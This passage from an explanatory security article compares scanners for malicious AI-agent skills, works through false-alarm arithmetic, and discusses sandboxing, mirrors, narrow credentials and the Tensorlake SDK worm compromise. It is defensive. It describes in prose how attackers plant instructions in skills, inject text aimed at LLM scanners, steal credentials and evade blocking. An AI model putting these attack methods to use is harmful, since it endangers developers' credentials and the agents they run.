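| Sentry, rules and language model | 98.4% | 23.4% |
| Cisco, rules and language model | 92.7% | 36.6% |
| AI-Infra-Guard (Tencent), language model | 86.6% | 15.5% |
| Cisco, rules only | 35.6% | 9.6% |
| Sentry, rules only | 28.7% | 13.7% |
| Snyk | 28.7% | 2.1% |
| VirusTotal | 21.6% | 0.1% |

Language models detect malicious skills much better than rules do because the same step can be legitimate in one skill and malicious in another. For example, asking for a server's password makes sense in a skill that publishes a website, but not in one that summarises videos. However, language models also flag many legitimate skills that install helper programs or ask for tokens.

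Attacks made only of plain-language instructions are the hardest to catch. AI-Infra-Guard caught 74.8% of them, compared with 99.2% of attacks in code. It caught only 35.8% of attacks that inserted false or biased content into the agent's answers.

To calculate false-alarm rates, the researchers assumed that ClawHub's most downloaded skills were harmless, partly because they had passed the registry's screening. VirusTotal does much of that screening, so the harmless set was very unlikely to include skills it had blocked. Its false-alarm rate of 0.1% is therefore probably too low.

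VirusTotal's detection rate also depends heavily on the test set. It was 21.6% overall but 87.9% on the 703 skills found in the wild, because most of those came from campaigns like ClawHavoc that deliver ordinary malware, which antivirus services recognise. VirusTotal caught three of the 33 wild skills that stole credentials directly.

Scanners made for ordinary packages don't reliably separate malicious skills from harmless ones. Microsoft's OSSGadget caught 97.3% of the malicious skills but also flagged almost 90% of the harmless ones. Datadog's GuardDog flagged only 49 harmless skills but caught just 15.4% of the malicious ones.

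A scanner that uses a language model has to read the attacker's text, which may contain instructions meant for the scanner. Tencent's Yang and colleagues therefore designed AI-Infra-Guard to treat everything it audits as untrusted. They still prefer fixed rules for recognising software with known flaws, because they are faster and give the same answer every time.

*SkillGate* (Yang, Fu and colleagues, July 2026) combines the two methods to save money. It first searches a skill for 530 text patterns. If it finds none, as happened with two-thirds of the test files, it passes the skill without using a language model. Otherwise it sends the model only the passages around the matches. In a test on 150 malicious and 1,500 harmless skills, it caught 76.9% of the malicious ones and flagged 1.13% of the harmless ones, taking an average of 0.8 seconds per skill.

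The patterns alone caught 90% of the malicious skills but flagged 27.1% of the harmless ones. The language model removed nearly all the false alarms but also let through about 20 more attacks. All 150 malicious skills were handmade, and the researchers assumed an attacker who doesn't know about SkillGate. SkillGate is open source, so a real attacker could download it and test a skill against it before publishing.

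The SkillGate test also included Cisco's scanner, with the same language model as in *MalSkillBench*. This time it caught only 18.0% of the malicious skills and flagged 0.73% of the harmless ones. Much of the difference probably comes from the threshold, because the SkillGate test counted only alarms that the scanner graded as critical. Either pair of figures alone would mislead a buyer about the product.

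### How many alarms are right

Suppose a registry has 10,000 skills, of which 1.9% are malicious, the share that Snyk confirmed in February. The registry scans them all with Sentry's scanner, the one with the highest detection rate in *MalSkillBench*:

```
190 malicious skills  × 98.4% ≈   187 correct alarms
9,810 harmless skills × 23.4% ≈ 2,296 false alarms

187 ÷ (187 + 2,296) ≈ 7.5% of alarms are correct
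```

Only about one alarm in 13 flags a skill that is actually malicious, even though the scanner misses three malicious skills. If a person needs ten minutes to check each alarm, the registry needs more than ten weeks of full-time work to check them all.

At SkillGate's rates, the same registry would get about 146 correct alarms and 111 false ones, so 57% of alarms would be correct, but 44 malicious skills would get through. The 57% is uncertain because SkillGate's language model doesn't always give the same answer. Its three test runs produced between 7 and 24 false alarms, which would put the share of correct alarms anywhere from 48% to 76%.

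The result also depends on how common malicious skills are. At 0.16%, the share in Liu and colleagues' study, the registry would have 16 malicious skills. SkillGate would catch about 12 of them and raise 113 false alarms, so only about one alarm in ten would be right.

The noisy scanner is more practical for the shop than for the registry. If the shop installs five skills a month, Sentry's scanner will raise about one false alarm a month, and the developer can read that skill before deciding. But after a year of false alarms, the developer may stop reading flagged skills and install them anyway.

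### Limiting the damage

Confinement starts from the assumption that something malicious has got past the scanner. The shop's agent needs only the mailbox, the order records and a model, so the shop can block access to the developer's SSH keys, the payment system and most of the internet.

An organization can keep an internal mirror, which holds its own copies of the models, packages and skills it has approved, and have its machines install only from there. A malicious release on npm then can't reach the agent until somebody copies it into the mirror. The mirror is also a convenient place to check hashes and enforce a cooldown. Somebody has to keep it up to date, including with urgent security fixes. Attackers can also target the mirror software itself, as happened when OpenAI's test agents got onto the internet through a flaw in a mirror.

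Once an artifact is running, the operating system can isolate it. A mailbox server in a container that holds only the server's own files can't read the passwords saved in the developer's browser. A virtual machine is usually a stronger barrier because it runs its own copy of the operating system's core, while containers share the host's. But it uses more memory and takes longer to start.

Help Net Security's *Week in review* (2026) reports that in October AWS, Amazon's cloud business, released Strands Box, a sandbox for agents that adds rules based on what the agent has already done. Such a rule could let an agent browse the web or open customer records, but stop it from contacting a new website once it has opened the records. Strands Box is still a preview and runs only on Macs with Apple processors.

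Isolation protects only what is outside the container, so the credentials inside it matter. Michael Scott, security chief at the data company Immuta, told Help Net Security that agents should be lower-trust identities that don't inherit everything their user can access. For the shop, that means giving the agent a mailbox token that can only read support mail and write drafts.

The spread from LiteLLM to telnyx shows why a credential's lifetime matters too. Help Net Security's *TeamPCP strikes again* (2026) quotes Kiran Raj of the security company Endor Labs, who thinks the attackers found telnyx's publishing token on a machine that had LiteLLM installed. The malicious telnyx releases came three days after the LiteLLM ones, which Raj thinks gave the attackers time to sort through the stolen data. A token that expired after an hour would have been useless by then. According to Akamai's *The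 Telnyx SDK on PyPI Compromise* (2026), telnyx has since switched to Trusted Publishing, which uses short-lived credentials.

Short token lifetimes do much less against malware that is still running, because it can take each new token as it arrives. Narrow permissions also have a limit. The postmark-mcp server stole email using only the permission to send email, which it needed to do its job.

Restricting outbound connections can stop stolen data from leaving. SC Media's *MemTensor npm, PyPI packages compromised with cross-platform credential stealer* describes a hijacked plugin that gives OpenClaw agents a memory. The malware started when the agent's gateway started, ran again whenever a user's prompt made the agent recall a memory, and exposed those prompts to the attacker. SC Media advises defenders to block the attacker's domain, but they can do that only after someone has identified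 it. A short list of permitted destinations would have blocked the connection from the start. Such a list would be workable for the shop's support agent but not for an agent that researches on the open web.

The shop can also move its tool servers off the developer's laptop, as FutureSearch did after the LiteLLM attack. A malicious update to the mailbox server could then steal the mailbox token but not the laptop's keys. If another company runs the server, the shop has to trust that company with its customers' mail.

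### The Tensorlake release

Tensorlake offers a cloud service that runs AI agents, and the code they write, in isolated environments. Developers control it through a software development kit (SDK) installed from npm. Socket's *TensorLake npm SDK Compromised in ChainDrop Shai-Hulud Credential-Stealing Attack* (8 October 2026) reported that version 0.5.144 of the SDK contained a credential-stealing variant of the Shai-Hulud worm.

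As the law firm Mishcon de Reya explains in *Shai-Hulud Burrows Into The Software Supply Chain* (2026), the attackers' malware ran during installation, before anyone had started an isolated environment, and did not break Tensorlake's isolation. It ran on developers' computers, servers and build machines, so a developer who bought the product to contain untrusted code could lose every credential on the laptop without running an agent.

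According to The Hacker News' *Tensorlake npm Package Compromised to Deliver Shai-Hulud Credential-Stealing Worm* (2026), the malware collected publishing tokens, cloud credentials and SSH keys, along with the settings of Claude, Cursor and other AI tools. Those settings include the MCP configuration, where the invented shop keeps its mailbox token. Like the testmetest worm, the malware also added start-up commands for coding tools to any projects it could reach.

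A check of the package's origin would probably have passed, because the attackers put their files in Tensorlake's own repository under a maintainer's name, and the project's normal release workflow published them a day later. Blocking the attackers' address would not have worked for long, because the malware looked up the address in a record that they could change at any time. If that failed, the malware could upload the stolen data to a public repository on GitHub, which most developers' machines need to reach.

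Mishcon de Reya reports that the release was detected about 11 minutes after publication and that the package usually gets 12,000 downloads a week. At that average rate, it would have been downloaded about 13 times before detection. The total was probably higher because npm removed the release some time later. A worm can spread from even a few infected machines.

Developers would have needed to confine the installation as well as the agent. They could install new versions in a disposable container without credentials, or set npm to skip installation scripts. Disabling scripts breaks some legitimate packages, and it doesn't help if the attacker puts the malware in the SDK's main code, which runs when a program uses the SDK. A cooldown would have kept this version out.

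Mishcon de Reya advises victims to remove the malware before revoking the stolen GitHub token, because revoking the token first may cause the malware to wipe the user's home folder, as with some versions of testmetest.

### Who should do the work

Each of these measures inconveniences users. Strict loaders reject some harmless models, false alarms take time to check, and a mirror delays updates. Confinement also makes the agent less useful, because people want agents that can install a missing package, look something up and send a reply. A large company can assign staff to handle approvals and exceptions, but at the shop this work falls to its only developer.

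There is no agreement on how to divide this work. The argument for giving it to registries is that one scan protects every user, and only the registry can remove a malicious skill for everyone. The objection is that scanners raise false alarms. If ClawHub blocked everything that Sentry's scanner flags, it would lose nearly a quarter of the popular skills in *MalSkillBench*, and their publishers would have to appeal. A registry is therefore likely to block only what a scanner with few false alarms flags, and to let most plain-language attacks through.

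Agent developers set the defaults, so they can run every new skill in a container unless the user chooses otherwise. This protects people who never open the settings. Developers have a commercial reason not to do it, since an agent that fails at a task because of a sandbox looks worse than a rival that succeeds without one. SkillGate is an attempt to add the protection from outside the agent. It sits between the agent and the source of its skills and works with five popular coding agents after a one-line change to their settings, but someone still has to install it.

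After the attack on the coding agent Cline, Henrik Plate of Endor Labs said that maintainers should turn on Trusted Publishing and disable the old tokens, and that users should notice when a package's attestations suddenly disappear (The Hacker News, *Cline CLI 2.3.0 Supply Chain Attack Installed OpenClaw on Developer Systems*, 2026). The advice to maintainers is realistic because a project needs to change its settings only once. Users can't reasonably watch the attestations of every package an agent installs, so in practice this job falls to the developers of the installers. Users still have to choose which credentials to give an agent, because nobody else knows which ones it needs.
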